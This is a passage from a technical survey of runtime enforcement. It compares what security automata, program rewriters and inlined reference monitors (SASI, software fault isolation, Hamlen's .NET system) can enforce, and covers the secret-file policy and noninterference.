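They require any such monitor to be sound and transparent. A sound monitor's output always satisfies the policy. A transparent monitor's output is equivalent to the program's own sequence whenever that sequence already satisfies the policy. What counts as equivalent depends on the system. For instance, closing a file twice may count as the same as closing it once.

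The extra powers don't let a monitor enforce any more policies if transparency has to hold event by event, so that the monitor passes on each event of a compliant run before it considers the next. Suppose a bad sequence could continue into a good one. The monitor has to change the bad sequence, because the program might stop there, but then it can no longer pass on the good one unchanged. Under this requirement, and with no advance knowledge of the program, all four types enforce exactly the safety properties.

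The types of automata differ in what they can enforce when the output only has to be equivalent in the end. For example, suppose a system requires an authenticated login, and a plain login followed by an authenticated one has the same effect as the authenticated one alone. A suppression automaton can drop the plain login and wait. A truncation automaton can't enforce this policy, because if it allows the plain login, the authenticated one may never come, and if it terminates the program, it may cut off a compliant run. On a San Francisco cable car, passengers must show a ticket before or after boarding, and showing it twice does no harm. An insertion automaton can enforce this policy by adding a "show ticket" event whenever someone boards without having shown a ticket.

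Edit automata can enforce far more policies because they can hold events back and release them later. Suppose a market requires every taking of apples to come with a payment for the same number, in either order. A program pays for three apples, browses for a while, and then takes three apples. The edit automaton holds back the payment and lets the browsing through. When the program takes the apples, the automaton releases the payment and the taking together. If the program had stopped after paying, no payment would have gone out, and the output would still have satisfied the policy. A suppression automaton could hold back the payment but not release it later, and an insertion automaton could not hold it back at all.

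With this method, the automaton can enforce every computable test on single executions, provided that all executions are finite and the empty sequence is valid. It releases everything it has held whenever the whole sequence so far passes the test, so it outputs a valid sequence unchanged and cuts an invalid one back to its longest valid prefix. If the empty sequence were invalid, the automaton would be in violation before it released anything.

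### Executions that never end

A monitor can't wait for an infinite execution to end, so it needs enough opportunities along the way to release the actions it is holding back. *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2005) identified a large class of policies that provide these opportunities, called infinite renewal properties. A policy is an infinite renewal property if every valid infinite execution has infinitely many valid prefixes and every invalid infinite execution has only finitely many.

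An edit automaton can enforce every such policy if the test for validity is decidable on finite sequences and the empty sequence passes it. In a valid infinite execution, every prefix is followed by a longer valid one, so the automaton eventually outputs every event. An invalid infinite execution has a last valid prefix, and the automaton outputs that prefix and never releases anything after it.

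The class contains every safety property, since every prefix of a valid execution is valid under a safety property. It also contains policies that Schneider's monitor cannot enforce. One such policy requires any program that does anything to perform an audit eventually. The automaton holds back all events until the audit occurs, then releases them, and every prefix from then on is valid. Similarly, a sequence of database operations is invalid halfway through a transaction and valid again at the end. Databases have long used a similar method, writing intended changes to a separate file and applying them only when the transaction completes.

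Some reasonable policies fall outside the class. One such policy requires a program with two resources to eventually close every resource it opens. The program could open 1, open 2, close 1, open 1, close 2, open 2, close 1 and so on forever. It eventually closes each resource it opens, so the execution is valid. But at least one resource is open at every moment after the start, so no prefix except the empty one is valid, and the automaton would never release any actions. With a single resource the problem disappears, because every close completes a valid prefix.

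An automaton that monitors execution cannot enforce the policy "the program terminates". Every finite prefix of a nonterminating run is itself a valid terminating run, so the automaton would keep releasing events forever.

Edit automata can also enforce some policies that are not renewal properties. If the events so far leave only one valid continuation and the automaton can compute it, the automaton can stop reading the program's events and output that continuation itself. Ligatti and colleagues add this exception to the renewal properties to obtain the exact class of policies that edit automata can enforce when they must output valid sequences unchanged. They consider the exception of little importance.

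A more serious limitation is that a monitor that holds back an event has to let the program continue as if the event had happened. Ligatti and colleagues give the example of an email, where the monitor can't wait for the reply before deciding whether to send the email, because there will be no reply until it is sent. Other events have a different effect if they happen later, and some require a secret key that the monitor doesn't have.

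*Runtime Enforcement With Partial Control* (Khoury and Hallé, 2018) builds these differences into the theory by sorting events according to whether the monitor can suppress them, insert them, do both, or do neither. For example, a monitor can usually prevent an email from being sent but cannot compose one on the program's behalf, and it can add a delay but cannot remove a past one. Buffering works only if the monitor can both suppress and insert every event it holds back on the way to the next valid prefix. If no event is both suppressible and insertable, buffering adds nothing. Khoury and Hallé therefore regard the renewal properties as an upper bound on what monitors can enforce in practice.

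This seems right for most programs that interact with the outside world. A program that reads a file needs the contents before it can continue, and one that queries a server needs the answer. Buffering is most useful where the monitor controls the system that carries out the events, as in a database.

### Advance knowledge and limited memory

Schneider's monitor is designed for programs in which any event could come next. A monitor can enforce more policies if it is designed for programs in which some sequences cannot occur, perhaps because a static analysis or an earlier change to the program has ruled them out. Suppose the policy requires a program to close every resource before it exits, and a tool has already inserted the closing operations at every exit. Opening a resource violates the policy until the resource is closed, so Schneider's monitor would have to block it. A monitor designed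 for the modified program can allow it. Even a truncation automaton can therefore enforce some policies that are not safety properties, although in this example the inserted code is what closes the resources.

Ligatti and colleagues also describe programs that always acquire a resource, use it at most twice, and release it. An administrator then decides to allow only one use. Terminating the program at the second use would leave the resource unreleased. A suppression automaton can drop the second use and let the program continue to the release, which always follows. An insertion automaton can add a release at that point and then terminate the program.

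Limiting what a monitor can store can also reduce the set of policies it can enforce. *Access Control By Tracking Shallow Execution History* (Fong, 2004) uses this limit to divide the enforceable policies into finer classes. Its main example is the shallow history automaton, which records which events have occurred but not their order or number. This automaton can enforce the rule about files and messages, since it only needs to know whether a file has been read. It can also enforce a Chinese Wall policy, under which someone who has accessed one company's data may not access a competitor's. It cannot enforce "at most three login attempts", because its record is the same after one attempt as after three.

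Fong proved that monitors with strictly more memory can enforce strictly more policies. Monitors that can tell any two prefixes apart are at the top of this ordering, and monitors with no memory of past events, which can only prohibit a fixed set of events, are at the bottom. A monitor with no memory can enforce the boot-sector policy even though that policy is undecidable, so how hard a policy is to decide in advance is a poor guide to how much a monitor has to store. Fong assumes finite executions and puts no limit on what a monitor can compute, so these results do not fit directly into the 2006 classification.

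### Edit automata and program rewriters

Hamlen and colleagues conjectured in 2006 that edit automata can enforce only a subset of the policies that program rewriters can, because a rewriter could build an edit automaton into the program. A rewriter has to turn every program into one that satisfies the policy, and it has to keep the behavior of already compliant programs equivalent. The basic argument, as reconstructed here, is that if an edit automaton enforces the policy, the rewriter could produce a new program that simulates the original together with the automaton and carries out only the events that the automaton releases.

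The automaton is sound, so every execution of the new program passes the test, and the new program therefore satisfies the policy. If the original program already satisfied the policy, all its executions passed the test. In that case, because the automaton is transparent, each execution of the new program is equivalent to the original program's execution on the same input.

The hard part is showing that the new program can hold events back. In the 2006 model, a trace begins with the program's own text and then records each input symbol as the program reads it. A rewritten program has a different text, so its trace can never be identical to the original's. The argument therefore needs a program equivalence and a detector that both ignore the changed text and the delays from buffering. The 2005 theorem about renewal properties covers what edit automata can do with infinite executions, but it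 treats executions as sequences of actions, with no program text or record of inputs, so it does not supply this step.

Even if the conjecture holds, rewriters can enforce policies that edit automata cannot, such as the secret-file policy. That policy compares what a program does with what it would have done if the file were not there, but an edit automaton works on only one execution at a time.

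## Program rewriting and inlined reference monitors

A program rewriter takes the text of any program *M* and returns, in finite time, another program *R*(*M*) that runs in its place. The practice is much older than the theory. *SASI Enforcement of Security Policies* (Erlingsson and Schneider, 1999) traces it to 1969, when a time-sharing system at Berkeley used modified machine code for security and monitoring.

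Hamlen and colleagues count a policy *P* as enforceable by rewriting if some rewriter *R* meets two conditions for every program *M*:

- RW1: *P*(*R*(*M*)). The output satisfies the policy, whatever the original program does.
- RW2: *P*(*M*) ⇒ *M* ≈ *R*(*M*). If the original program already satisfied the policy, the output is equivalent to it.

*R* must be an algorithm that returns a program for every input. Its extra power comes from never having to report whether *M* satisfied the policy.

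RW2 places no requirement on programs that violate the policy. Even if a program violates the policy on only one input in a million, a rewriter may replace it with a program that prints an error message and stops. Most real rewriters preserve the program's behavior until it is about to do something forbidden. *Inlined Reference Monitors: Certification, Concurrency and Tree Based Monitoring*, a thesis on inserting checks into programs, lists conservativity as a third requirement, alongside security (roughly RW1) and transparency (roughly RW2). Conservativity means that the inserted code adds no behavior of its own.

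### Which programs count as equivalent

The symbol ≈ in RW2 stands for program equivalence. Hamlen and colleagues call two programs equivalent if, on every input, their executions are equivalent. They leave open what makes two executions equivalent, and this choice largely determines what a rewriter can do.

At one extreme, two programs are equivalent only if their texts are identical. A rewriter must then return every compliant program unchanged, so it can't insert checks into one. At the other extreme, all programs are equivalent. RW2 is then always true, and a rewriter can ignore its input and return the same compliant program every time. This would technically enforce every policy that at least one program satisfies, however hard the policy is to compute, but it would discard whatever useful work the original program did.

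A useful equivalence lies in between. For example, it might require the same outputs in the same order but ignore the extra steps that inserted checks take.

The choice of equivalence also limits which detectors make sense. A detector is consistent with an equivalence if it never passes one execution and rejects another that is equivalent to it. Consistency matters because rewriters treat equivalent executions as interchangeable, which would be a mistake if one were acceptable and the other forbidden. A detector that forbids sending a message after reading a file is inconsistent with an equivalence that ignores the order of events, because sending first and reading afterwards is allowed. A detector that counts steps is inconsistent with an equivalence that ignores extra steps. If all executions are equivalent, a consistent detector must pass all of them or reject all of them, which rules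 out the useless rewriter for any detector of interest.

Hamlen and colleagues point out that real rewriting systems typically assume very complicated definitions of equivalence and leave most of them unstated. Until someone writes these definitions down, no one can say exactly which policies such a system enforces.

### When rewriting adds something to static analysis

A rewriter can enforce every policy that a static analysis can, provided at least one program satisfies the policy. To prove this, let *S* be a program that satisfies the policy, perhaps one that prints an error message and stops. The rewriter runs the static analysis on the input program *M*. If the analysis accepts *M*, the rewriter returns *M* unchanged. Otherwise, it returns *S*.

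The rewriter always finishes because the analysis does. RW1 holds because the rewriter returns only *S* or a program that has passed the analysis. RW2 holds because the rewriter returns compliant programs unchanged, and every program is equivalent to itself. The one exception is the policy that no program satisfies. A static analysis can enforce it by rejecting every program, but a rewriter can't, because it has to return some program and every program violates the policy.

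Under some equivalences, rewriting can do no more than this. Suppose an algorithm can decide whether any two programs are equivalent, and suppose a rewriter *R* enforces a policy induced by a consistent detector. Then a static analysis can enforce the policy too. Given *M*, it computes *R*(*M*) and decides whether the two programs are equivalent:

- If they are not, *M* violates the policy, because RW2 guarantees that a compliant program is equivalent to its rewritten version.
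- If they are, *M* satisfies the policy. By RW1, every execution of *R*(*M*) passes the detector. On each input, *M*'s execution is equivalent to *R*(*M*)'s, so by consistency it passes as well.

Both steps take finite time, so this procedure decides the policy. Rewriting is therefore worth considering for such policies only if equivalence is undecidable.

The usual notions of program equivalence, such as giving the same output on every input, are undecidable. Rewriting is still possible because a rewriter only has to make changes that its designers know will preserve the behavior of compliant programs, and never has to compare two arbitrary programs.

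### The boot-sector rewriter

The boot-sector policy is an example of what rewriting adds. No static analysis can enforce it, but a rewriter can turn any program *M* into a program *M′* that does the following before each step of *M*:

1. *M′* simulates the step once for every input symbol that *M* might read next.
2. If any of these simulations writes to one of cells 0 to 511, *M′* halts.
3. Otherwise, *M′* carries out the step.

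*M′* also has to keep its own working data out of those cells. RW1 holds because *M′* always halts before a forbidden write. RW2 holds because if *M* never writes to the boot sector on any input, the simulations never find a forbidden write. *M′* then does everything *M* does but takes more steps, so the equivalence has to ignore the extra steps. Constructing *M′* takes finite time because the rewriter only adds the look-ahead code and doesn't run the program.

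A certifying compiler, which produces machine code together with a proof that the code satisfies a policy, works similarly. If the source program complies, the compiler must preserve its behavior, as RW2 requires. If it doesn't, the compiler can reject it, which amounts to translating it into an empty program, or insert checks that change its behavior only where a violation would have occurred. The machine code complies in every case, as RW1 requires. Hamlen and colleagues conclude that, if source programs are taken as the programs in question, certifying compilers enforce exactly the policies that rewriters can.

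Inserting checks also gets around a limit of proof-carrying code. Some programs never write to the boot sector, but no proof of this exists in the consumer's logic. Their rewritten versions are much easier to prove safe. If a check comes before every step, the proof only has to show that the check works and that the program cannot avoid it, regardless of what the original program would have done.

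### Software fault isolation

One of the best-known uses of rewriting is to keep a program's writes and jumps within a fixed part of memory. Wahbe, Lucco and colleagues (1993) developed this technique in *Efficient Software-Based Fault Isolation* for applications that load extensions from other companies. For example, extensions to the desktop publishing program Quark Xpress could corrupt its internal data and make it crash, and users blamed Quark.

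The standard protection was to run each extension in its own address space, and the hardware kept the address spaces apart. But a call from one address space to another often took 100 to 1,000 times as long as an ordinary procedure call. Wahbe and colleagues instead put the extension in the same address space as the application and gave it two segments of memory, one for code and one for data. All addresses within a segment begin with the same bits, so these bits identify the segment.

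Some writes and jumps are easy to verify in advance because the instruction contains the target address. The rest need extra code. One version, segment matching, uses four instructions to extract the first bits of the address, compare them with the segment's, and stop the extension if they differ. This identifies the faulty instruction, which helps with debugging.

A faster version, called sandboxing, uses two instructions to overwrite the first bits of the address with those of the extension's data segment, instead of checking them. Suppose the segment contains the addresses that start with 15 in hexadecimal. A write to 2F001234 then becomes a write to 15001234, which can damage only the extension's own data. Writes to addresses already in the segment are unchanged.

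Sandboxing meets both conditions without detecting violations. A compliant extension behaves as before because its addresses already start with the right bits, and a faulty one keeps running but can't write outside its segment.

### Inlining a security automaton

Erlingsson and Schneider generalized this method from policies on memory addresses to any policy that a security automaton can express. Their system, SASI, inserts the automaton into the program's code, producing an inlined reference monitor.

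When a monitor runs outside the program, the processor has to switch from the program to the monitor and back for each event, which takes time. The monitor also receives control only at certain events, such as calls to the operating system. A web browser might need a rule about how its helper applications use the browser's resources, but if they do this through ordinary procedure calls, the relevant events never reach the operating system. Hamlen also notes in the lecture slides *Enforceability Theory* that changing the policy of a monitor inside the operating system means changing the operating system.

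SASI inserts the monitor in four phases:

1. It places a copy of the whole automaton before every instruction.
2. It specializes each copy to the instruction that follows, working out which transition conditions are already known to be true or false.
3. It deletes the transitions whose conditions are false.
4. It compiles what is left into guard code, which updates the automaton's state or stops the program if no transition is possible.

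Some conditions depend on values that exist only when the program runs, such as the address of a write. In these cases, the guard code computes the value at that point.

Erlingsson and Schneider illustrate the method with the policy that a program must push exactly one value onto the stack before it returns. The automaton starts in state 0, where the program has pushed nothing yet. A push takes it to state 1. The automaton has no transition for a return in state 0 or a second push in state 1, and all other instructions leave the state unchanged.

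The program to rewrite is a routine that squares the number in register r0, pushes the result and returns:

```
mul  r1, r0, r0
push r1
ret
```

Specializing the automaton to each of these instructions gives the following:

| Instruction | In state 0 | In state 1 | Guard code |
|---|---|---|---|
| mul | stay in state 0 | stay in state 1 | none |
| push | go to state 1 | no transition | if the state is 0, set it to 1, otherwise abort |
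| ret | no transition | stay in state 1 | if the state is 0, abort |

Multiplication never changes the state and is never forbidden, so it needs no guard. The rewritten routine is:

```
mul  r1, r0, r0
if state == 0 then state := 1 else ABORT
push r1
if state == 0 then ABORT
ret
```

The last check is unnecessary if the program can reach the return only by running the instructions before it, because the state is then always 1. SASI leaves the check in because it considers only one instruction at a time. Erlingsson and Schneider chose not to add a wider analysis because it would have made the rewriter larger and more complicated, and any mistake in it could make the policy ineffective.

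SASI has one version for Intel's x86 processors and another for Java bytecode, the compiled form of Java programs. To enforce the rule against sending messages after reading a file, the Java version inserts code only before calls that read a file or send a message. The code before each read sets a variable, and the code before each send checks that variable and stops the program if it has been set.

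Erlingsson and Schneider concluded that neither version could become a practical tool. The policy language could not store a string, for instance, so it was awkward to require a program to use the same file name in several operations. A more basic problem with the x86 version was that machine code doesn't mark function calls, so policy writers had to describe the instruction patterns that make up a call.

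Their next system therefore worked only with Java bytecode, which contains this information. Users write policies in a Java-like language called PSLang, and a rewriter called PoET inserts them into programs. *Policy-Carrying, Policy-Enforcing Digital Objects* (Payette and Lagoze, 2000) used PoET in a digital library where each item carries its own policy. For example, the policy for a recorded lecture might let everyone see the first ten slides but restrict the rest to members of Cornell University.

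### Keeping the program from defeating its monitor

An inlined monitor shares memory and code with the program it is supposed to control. A malicious program can attack it by jumping past a check, changing the monitor's variables, or running new code that contains no checks.

If a program containing the squaring routine jumps directly to the push instruction, it skips the guard. On x86 processors, a program can also jump into the middle of an instruction, where the remaining bytes may form a different, forbidden instruction. SASI prevents both by allowing jumps only to labels that the compiler has listed.

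Wahbe and colleagues solved the problem with dedicated registers, which only the inserted code may change. The rewriter makes each unsafe write take its address from a dedicated register, which always holds an address in the right segment. The write therefore goes to the extension's own memory even if the program jumps past the sandboxing code. Sandboxing takes up five registers, which did not significantly affect speed on a processor with 32 registers but is a problem on processors with few. McCamant and Morrisett later developed a different technique for 32-bit x86 processors.

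The x86 version of SASI protects the monitor's variables by adding a memory-protection policy to whatever policy the user wants to enforce. The same inserted code then protects both the program's surroundings and the monitor itself. Erlingsson and Schneider argue by contradiction that the monitor can protect itself this way. The first instruction to subvert the monitor would have to be a write, jump, call or return, and a guard comes before every one of these. Since nothing would have subverted the monitor before then, the guard would have run correctly and blocked the instruction.

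The argument depends on accurate information from the compiler, gcc, about which addresses and jump targets are valid. The Java version relies mostly on the type system instead. The names and types of the monitor's variables prevent the program from accessing them, and the program can't jump into the inserted code because that code contains no labels.

Code that appears only at run time needs separate treatment. The Java version of SASI had to forbid programs from loading new classes or using reflection, which lets a program inspect and call its own parts by name. Payette and Lagoze instead extended PoET to rewrite each new piece of code just before it runs. Vanoverberghe and Piessens note in *A Caller-Side Inline Reference Monitor for an Object-Oriented Intermediate Language* that finding every relevant event can be hard even without new code. In an object-oriented language, for instance,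 a call may name one class's method but run another's, depending on the object.

A monitor can also fail when a program has threads, which are parts of the program that run at the same time. Suppose two threads share the monitor's state and both are about to push a value. Each may read the state as 0 before either sets it to 1, and both pushes then go ahead. The monitor can prevent this by letting only one thread at a time perform a check together with the event it guards, but that restriction can change how a compliant program behaves.

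Hamlen's system for Microsoft's .NET platform had this problem. If two threads tried to use the same monitored object at the same time, one could terminate with an error because the object was unavailable, even though the program had not violated the policy. The rewriter still met RW1 but failed RW2 for some programs. Hamlen suggested making the second thread wait instead, but left this for later work.

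### Checking the output instead of trusting the rewriter

A good rewriter tends to be large, because it has to handle every feature of the language and still produce fast code. It is also easy to get wrong. For example, MiSFIT, a software fault isolation tool for x86 processors, temporarily saved a register on the stack while it checked an address. Erlingsson and Schneider noticed that a program writing to an array that overlapped the stack could overwrite the saved value.

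A separate, smaller tool can check each rewritten program for mistakes made by the rewriter. A mistake then leads to a rejected program rather than a security hole, so only the checker has to be trusted. Proof-carrying code also pairs an untrusted code producer with a trusted checker.

In Hamlen's .NET system, the rewriter wraps each monitored object in a package with a number that records the object's state. Before a relevant operation, the inserted code unpacks the object and tests the number. If the policy allows the operation, the code carries it out, updates the number and repacks the object. Otherwise, it raises an error. The rewriter also adds annotations that describe the possible states at points where different paths through the program meet. A type-checker checks the program one instruction at a time and accepts it only if the annotations are correct and show that the program follows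 the policy.

The rewriter had about 3,500 lines of code and the type-checker about 2,000. Around half of the type-checker repeated work that .NET already did, so Hamlen estimated that adding the type-checker to an existing system would increase the trusted code by only about 1,000 lines.

Hamlen's checker relies on one particular way of inserting the monitor. *A Proof Carrying Code Framework for Inlined Reference Monitors in Java Bytecode* (Dam and Lundblad, 2018) allows more ways. The program's recipient adds a "ghost" monitor, which exists only in annotations and never runs. The proof shows that the real monitor's state matches the ghost's at every relevant call.

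Such proofs would normally be hard to construct for a whole program. Dam and Lundblad avoid this by requiring each piece of inserted code to be continuous, and by allowing jumps into or out of it only when the two monitors agree. They also require the monitor's state to be stored where a simple scan can find every instruction that changes it. This makes it easy to see that the rest of the program can't affect the monitor, so only the inserted pieces need detailed proofs. They also proved the method sound in the proof assistant Coq.

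For software fault isolation, the check can be very simple. Wahbe and colleagues describe an algorithm that verifies whether a module is sandboxed correctly, and users can check the output of McCamant and Morrisett's technique when they load a program. Researchers also work on formally proving these small checkers correct. Tan's survey *Principles and Implementation Techniques of Software-Based Fault Isolation* covers this work in detail, and *Automated Formal Verification of a Software Fault Isolation System* (2025) is a recent example.

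Hamlen's type-checker and Dam and Lundblad's proofs establish that the output satisfies the policy (RW1), but they don't establish RW2. If a faulty rewriter replaced every program with an empty one, its output could pass the check under any policy that allows a program to do nothing. This failure is much less dangerous, though users would have to notice that their programs had stopped working.

### What the inserted code costs

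Sandboxing slowed programs by 4% on average in Wahbe and colleagues' tests, but a call between an extension and the application took about a microsecond, less than a tenth of the time the fastest alternatives needed. Software isolation is therefore most attractive when the two sides call each other often and most of the work happens in trusted code, which runs at full speed. In a test with the database system POSTGRES, it reduced the overhead of isolation by more than a factor of three. Tan also reports an overhead of less than 5% for software fault isolation.

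The cost can be much higher when the rewriter is more general or the program uses memory heavily. Erlingsson and Schneider compared SASI with MiSFIT by enforcing the same memory policy on three programs. The running times below are multiples of the original program's:

| Program | MiSFIT | SASI |
|---|---|---|
| Choosing which memory pages to remove | 2.38 | 3.64 |
| Simulated disk | 1.58 | 1.65 |
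| MD5 checksum | 1.33 | 1.36 |

MiSFIT does better partly because it enforces only this one policy and optimizes the code it inserts.

Java programs usually need fewer checks, because the type system already protects memory. Erlingsson and Schneider used SASI to reproduce the security checks built into Java 1.1 and found no statistical difference in overhead. A rewriter can also omit checks that are certain to succeed, whereas Java's built-in version always performed them. In *IRM enforcement of Java stack inspection* (2000), they implemented stack inspection, a more complex Java policy that decides whether to allow an operation based on which procedures led to it. One of their two implementations was competitive with Java's own.

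Hamlen tested the .NET system on a set of benchmarks with a policy that limits the number of calls to certain libraries. The limit was too high for any program to reach, so the test measured only the overhead of checking. The rewritten benchmarks took 17% longer in total. Most of this came from a single benchmark, whose running time nearly doubled because it made monitored calls inside its inner loops. When Hamlen moved some of the checks out of the loops by hand, the total overhead fell to 2.7%, and the type-checker still accepted the program. Checks written by hand without certification added 1.4%. Certification therefore added little to the running time, and the main problem was that the rewriter did not optimize its output. A small web server, rewritten to limit the number of connections, kept 99.97% of its original throughput.

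WebAssembly is probably the most widely used relative of software fault isolation. It is a format for compiled programs that browsers and servers run in a sandbox. Its compilers keep each program within its own memory, often by inserting bounds checks. Researchers have tried to speed up this isolation with Arm's Memory Tagging Extension, in which the processor labels blocks of memory and stops a program whose pointer has the wrong label.

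Such overheads are easy to misjudge. An earlier study reported that memory tagging made WebAssembly programs up to 1.34 times faster on a Google Pixel 8 phone. *ARM MTE Performance in Practice (Extended Version)* (2026) traced this result to a bug. In one benchmark, the earlier system correctly labeled only 16 of 784 pages of memory, so it enforced almost nothing. The paper measured slowdowns of up to 3.65 times on the same processors.

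If memory tagging is the only protection, it also slows down the trusted part of the application, unlike the 1993 design, because every page in the process needs a label. The ColorGuard system avoids this by using the labels on top of ordinary software fault isolation, which already separates the sandboxes from the rest of the process.

### Limits on time and program size

In the theory, a rewriter may take any finite amount of time, and its output may be enormously larger and slower than the original. Hamlen and colleagues proposed two restrictions for future study. One would limit the rewriter to time and memory that are constant or polynomial in the size of the program, and the other would limit how much larger and slower the rewritten program may be. They did not determine which policies remain enforceable under either restriction.

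Inlining a fixed, finite automaton with simple transition conditions meets both. The rewriter processes instructions one at a time and adds a limited amount of code to each, so the program's size and running time grow by at most a constant factor.

Rewriting a program to satisfy a policy can take far less computation than deciding whether it already does. For example, checking that a program terminates within 100 steps by trying every input takes about 2^100 runs. A rewriter can instead make about a hundred copies of the program's states, one for each number of steps taken so far, and have the last copy always halt. Every program it produces stops in time. A compliant program has already stopped by then, so it takes exactly the same steps as before. The new program is about a hundred times as large as the original, and the rewriter can produce it without running the original.

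## Policies that rewriting can enforce and monitoring cannot

The secret-file policy shows that a rewriter can do more than insert a monitor. It requires a program to behave exactly as it would if a secret file were missing from a directory. Hamlen and colleagues enforce it by adding code wherever the program retrieves a listing of the directory. The added code deletes the secret file's entry before the program can use the listing.

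Suppose the directory contains seven ordinary files and the secret one. A program that prints the number of files violates the policy, because it prints 8 and would print 7 without the secret file. After rewriting, it prints 7. A program that prints only the names ending in ".txt" complies if the secret file's name ends differently, and rewriting doesn't change its output.

Both conditions on a rewriter are easy to check:

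- RW1, that the output complies: the rewritten program gets the same listing whether or not the file exists, so it behaves the same way in both cases.
- RW2, that compliant programs keep their behavior: the rewritten program does what the original would do without the file. If the original complied, it does the same thing with the file.

A cruder rewriter could make every listing empty. It would meet RW1 but fail RW2, because the program that prints ".txt" names would no longer print any.

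### Enforcing a policy without detecting violations

The rewriter makes the same change to every program, without determining whether the program would have reacted to the secret file. The change affects only the programs that would have violated the policy. Sandboxing memory addresses works the same way, though a monitor could easily have checked those addresses instead. No monitor can check whether a program complies with the secret-file policy.

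The argument for RW1 assumes that the listing is the program's only source of information about the file, but real systems usually have others. A program might try to open the file by name and get the error "permission denied" instead of "no such file". It might try to create a file with the same name and fail, or compare the free space on the disk with the total size of the files it can see. The rewriter has to change each of these operations to return what it would if the file didn't exist. If the rewriter misses one, a program can still behave differently when the file exists, and RW1 fails.

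Some of these changes take more work than deleting an entry from a list. For instance, if the program creates a file with the same name as the secret file, the system has to store both files and keep them apart. The theory of rewriting can't show whether the rewriter has covered every channel, because that depends on the file system.

### Why a monitor cannot do the same

A monitor can enforce only coRE policies, for which an algorithm can find every violation in finite time. Whether the secret-file policy is coRE depends on what counts as the same behavior. Suppose first that only the program's output matters, regardless of delays.

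For any program *N* and input *x*, we can build a program *M* that retrieves the directory listing. If the secret file is missing, *M* prints "done" and halts. If the file is there, *M* first runs *N* on *x*, then prints "done" and halts. *M* therefore complies with the policy if *N* halts on *x*, because it prints "done" whether or not the file is there. If *N* runs forever, *M* prints "done" only when the file is missing, which violates the policy.

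An algorithm that detected every violation in finite time would therefore detect every computation that runs forever. Running it alongside *N* would solve the halting problem, so the policy is not coRE.

Hamlen and colleagues give a more general reason. Checking whether a program behaves equivalently on two inputs is as hard as checking whether two programs are equivalent on all inputs. Given any two programs, one can build a third that runs the first if the secret file exists and the second if it doesn't. The third program complies exactly when the first two are equivalent, and the usual notions of program equivalence are not coRE.

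Hamlen and colleagues explain that even a monitor with access to the program's text can't solve this problem by simulating the program twice, once with the file and once without, and comparing the results. Equivalent runs don't have to match step for step, so one simulation may produce an output long before the other. For example, one copy of *M* may print "done" while the other is still running *N*. Blocking the output would interfere with a compliant program if *N* is about to halt, but allowing it would reveal the file if *N* never halts. If the monitor waits for the second copy, it may wait forever.

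The rewriter doesn't have this problem with *M*. The rewritten program can't detect the secret file, so it prints "done" immediately. If *N* halts, *M* would have produced the same output. If *N* runs forever, *M* violated the policy, so RW2 doesn't apply.

### When the two runs must match at every step

The proof that the policy isn't coRE relies on ignoring delays, but an attacker who can time the program could learn about the file from a delay. Suppose the administrator prevents this by requiring the runs with and without the file to match at every step. When comparing them, we can treat retrieving the listing as a single step and ignore the listing's contents.

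If two such runs differ, they first differ after finitely many steps, when the program has read only finitely many input symbols. An algorithm can therefore find every violation by simulating both runs for one step, then two, and so on, trying every input the program could have read by then, so the stricter policy is coRE.

A monitor that has the program's text can make the same comparison while the program runs. Before each step, it simulates what the program would have done on the same input if the file didn't exist. The two runs read the same symbols at the same steps until they first differ, so the monitor always has the input it needs, and each comparison takes finite time. The monitor must also make the comparison when the file doesn't exist, by simulating a directory that contains it. Otherwise it would stop the program only when the file is there, and stopping would reveal that the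 file exists.

The stricter policy is easier to check, but it forbids many harmless programs. The program that prints ".txt" names takes a few extra steps to skip the secret file's entry, so it violates the stricter policy even though its output is the same. A compromise is to require each output to appear in both runs within, say, 1,000 steps of each other. This policy is also coRE, because the monitor never has to wait more than 1,000 steps for the slower run.

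### A policy at the Π₂ level

Fully formalizing the secret-file policy would require modeling the file system, so Hamlen and colleagues use a simpler policy, based on the universal machine *U*, to prove that some policies are enforceable by rewriting but not coRE. *U* takes the text of any program and an input, simulates the program on that input, and halts if and only if the program would.

In this proof, two programs are equivalent if they halt on exactly the same inputs. A program satisfies the policy if it is equivalent to *U*. The rewriter ignores the program it receives and always returns *U*. RW1 holds because *U* is equivalent to itself. RW2 holds because every compliant program is equivalent to *U* by definition.

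To show that the policy is not coRE, take any two programs *A* and *B*. Build a program *C* that works like *U*, except that when given *B* to simulate, it simulates *A* instead. If *A* and *B* halt on the same inputs, *C* is equivalent to *U*. Otherwise, there is an input on which only one of them halts, and *C* differs from *U* when given *B* to simulate on that input.

An algorithm that could decide which programs satisfy the policy could therefore decide whether any two programs halt on the same inputs. That problem is Π₂-complete, which means it is as hard as any problem in Π₂. The policy is Π₂-complete too, since deciding it is the same problem with *U* as one of the two programs. It is therefore not coRE, and no monitor can enforce it.

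This example proves the theorem but has no practical value, as Hamlen and colleagues acknowledge. The policy allows only one pattern of halting, so anyone who wanted a compliant program could run *U* and would have no use for the untrusted program. The equivalence also depends only on halting, so the rewriter would discard any useful results that a compliant program printed before it halted.

Hamlen's lecture slides give a more general version, the policy that untrusted code must behave identically to a given program on all inputs. It has the same drawback, because the rewriter can always return the given program. The secret-file policy is a much better argument for rewriting, because it allows programs to do many different things and the rewriter preserves whatever a compliant program does.

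### Noninterference

The secret-file policy is a hyperproperty, because it compares what a program does in different runs. It is also an example of noninterference, which requires that secret inputs make no difference to what an outsider can observe. (Rules about the purpose for which an AI agent may use data raise a similar problem.)

To define noninterference precisely, we label each input and output either public or secret. Let *I* and *I′* be two inputs to the program, and let *O* and *O′* be the corresponding outputs. A program is noninterfering if, for all such inputs:

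*I* and *I′* have the same public part ⇒ *O* and *O′* have the same public part.

Secret inputs may not affect public outputs, although public inputs may affect secret outputs. In the secret-file policy, the only secret input is whether the file exists, and all outputs are public.

*Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) gives an example from a web-based email program. A malicious script reads the email a user is writing and puts its text into the web address of a banner image on another company's server. When the script loads the image, the request sends the text to that company. The text is a secret input and the request is a public output.

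The script also leaks information indirectly. It sets a variable to 1 if the email contains the letters "abc" and leaves it at 0 otherwise, then adds the variable to the address. The variable's value depends on the email even though the script never copies the email into it. Other programs could reveal the same bit through timing, by running a long loop only if it is 1, or through termination, by looping forever before the request if it is 0.

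Static analyses and monitors can prevent such leaks, but only by also blocking some harmless programs. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (Algehed and Flanagan, 2020) reports that even the best implementations raise too many false alarms to manage. If the filter from the secret-file example hid the email's text from the whole program, nothing would leak, but the user could no longer send the email to its intended recipient. The policy allows a program to use a secret as long as the secret affects only secret outputs.

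### Secure multi-execution

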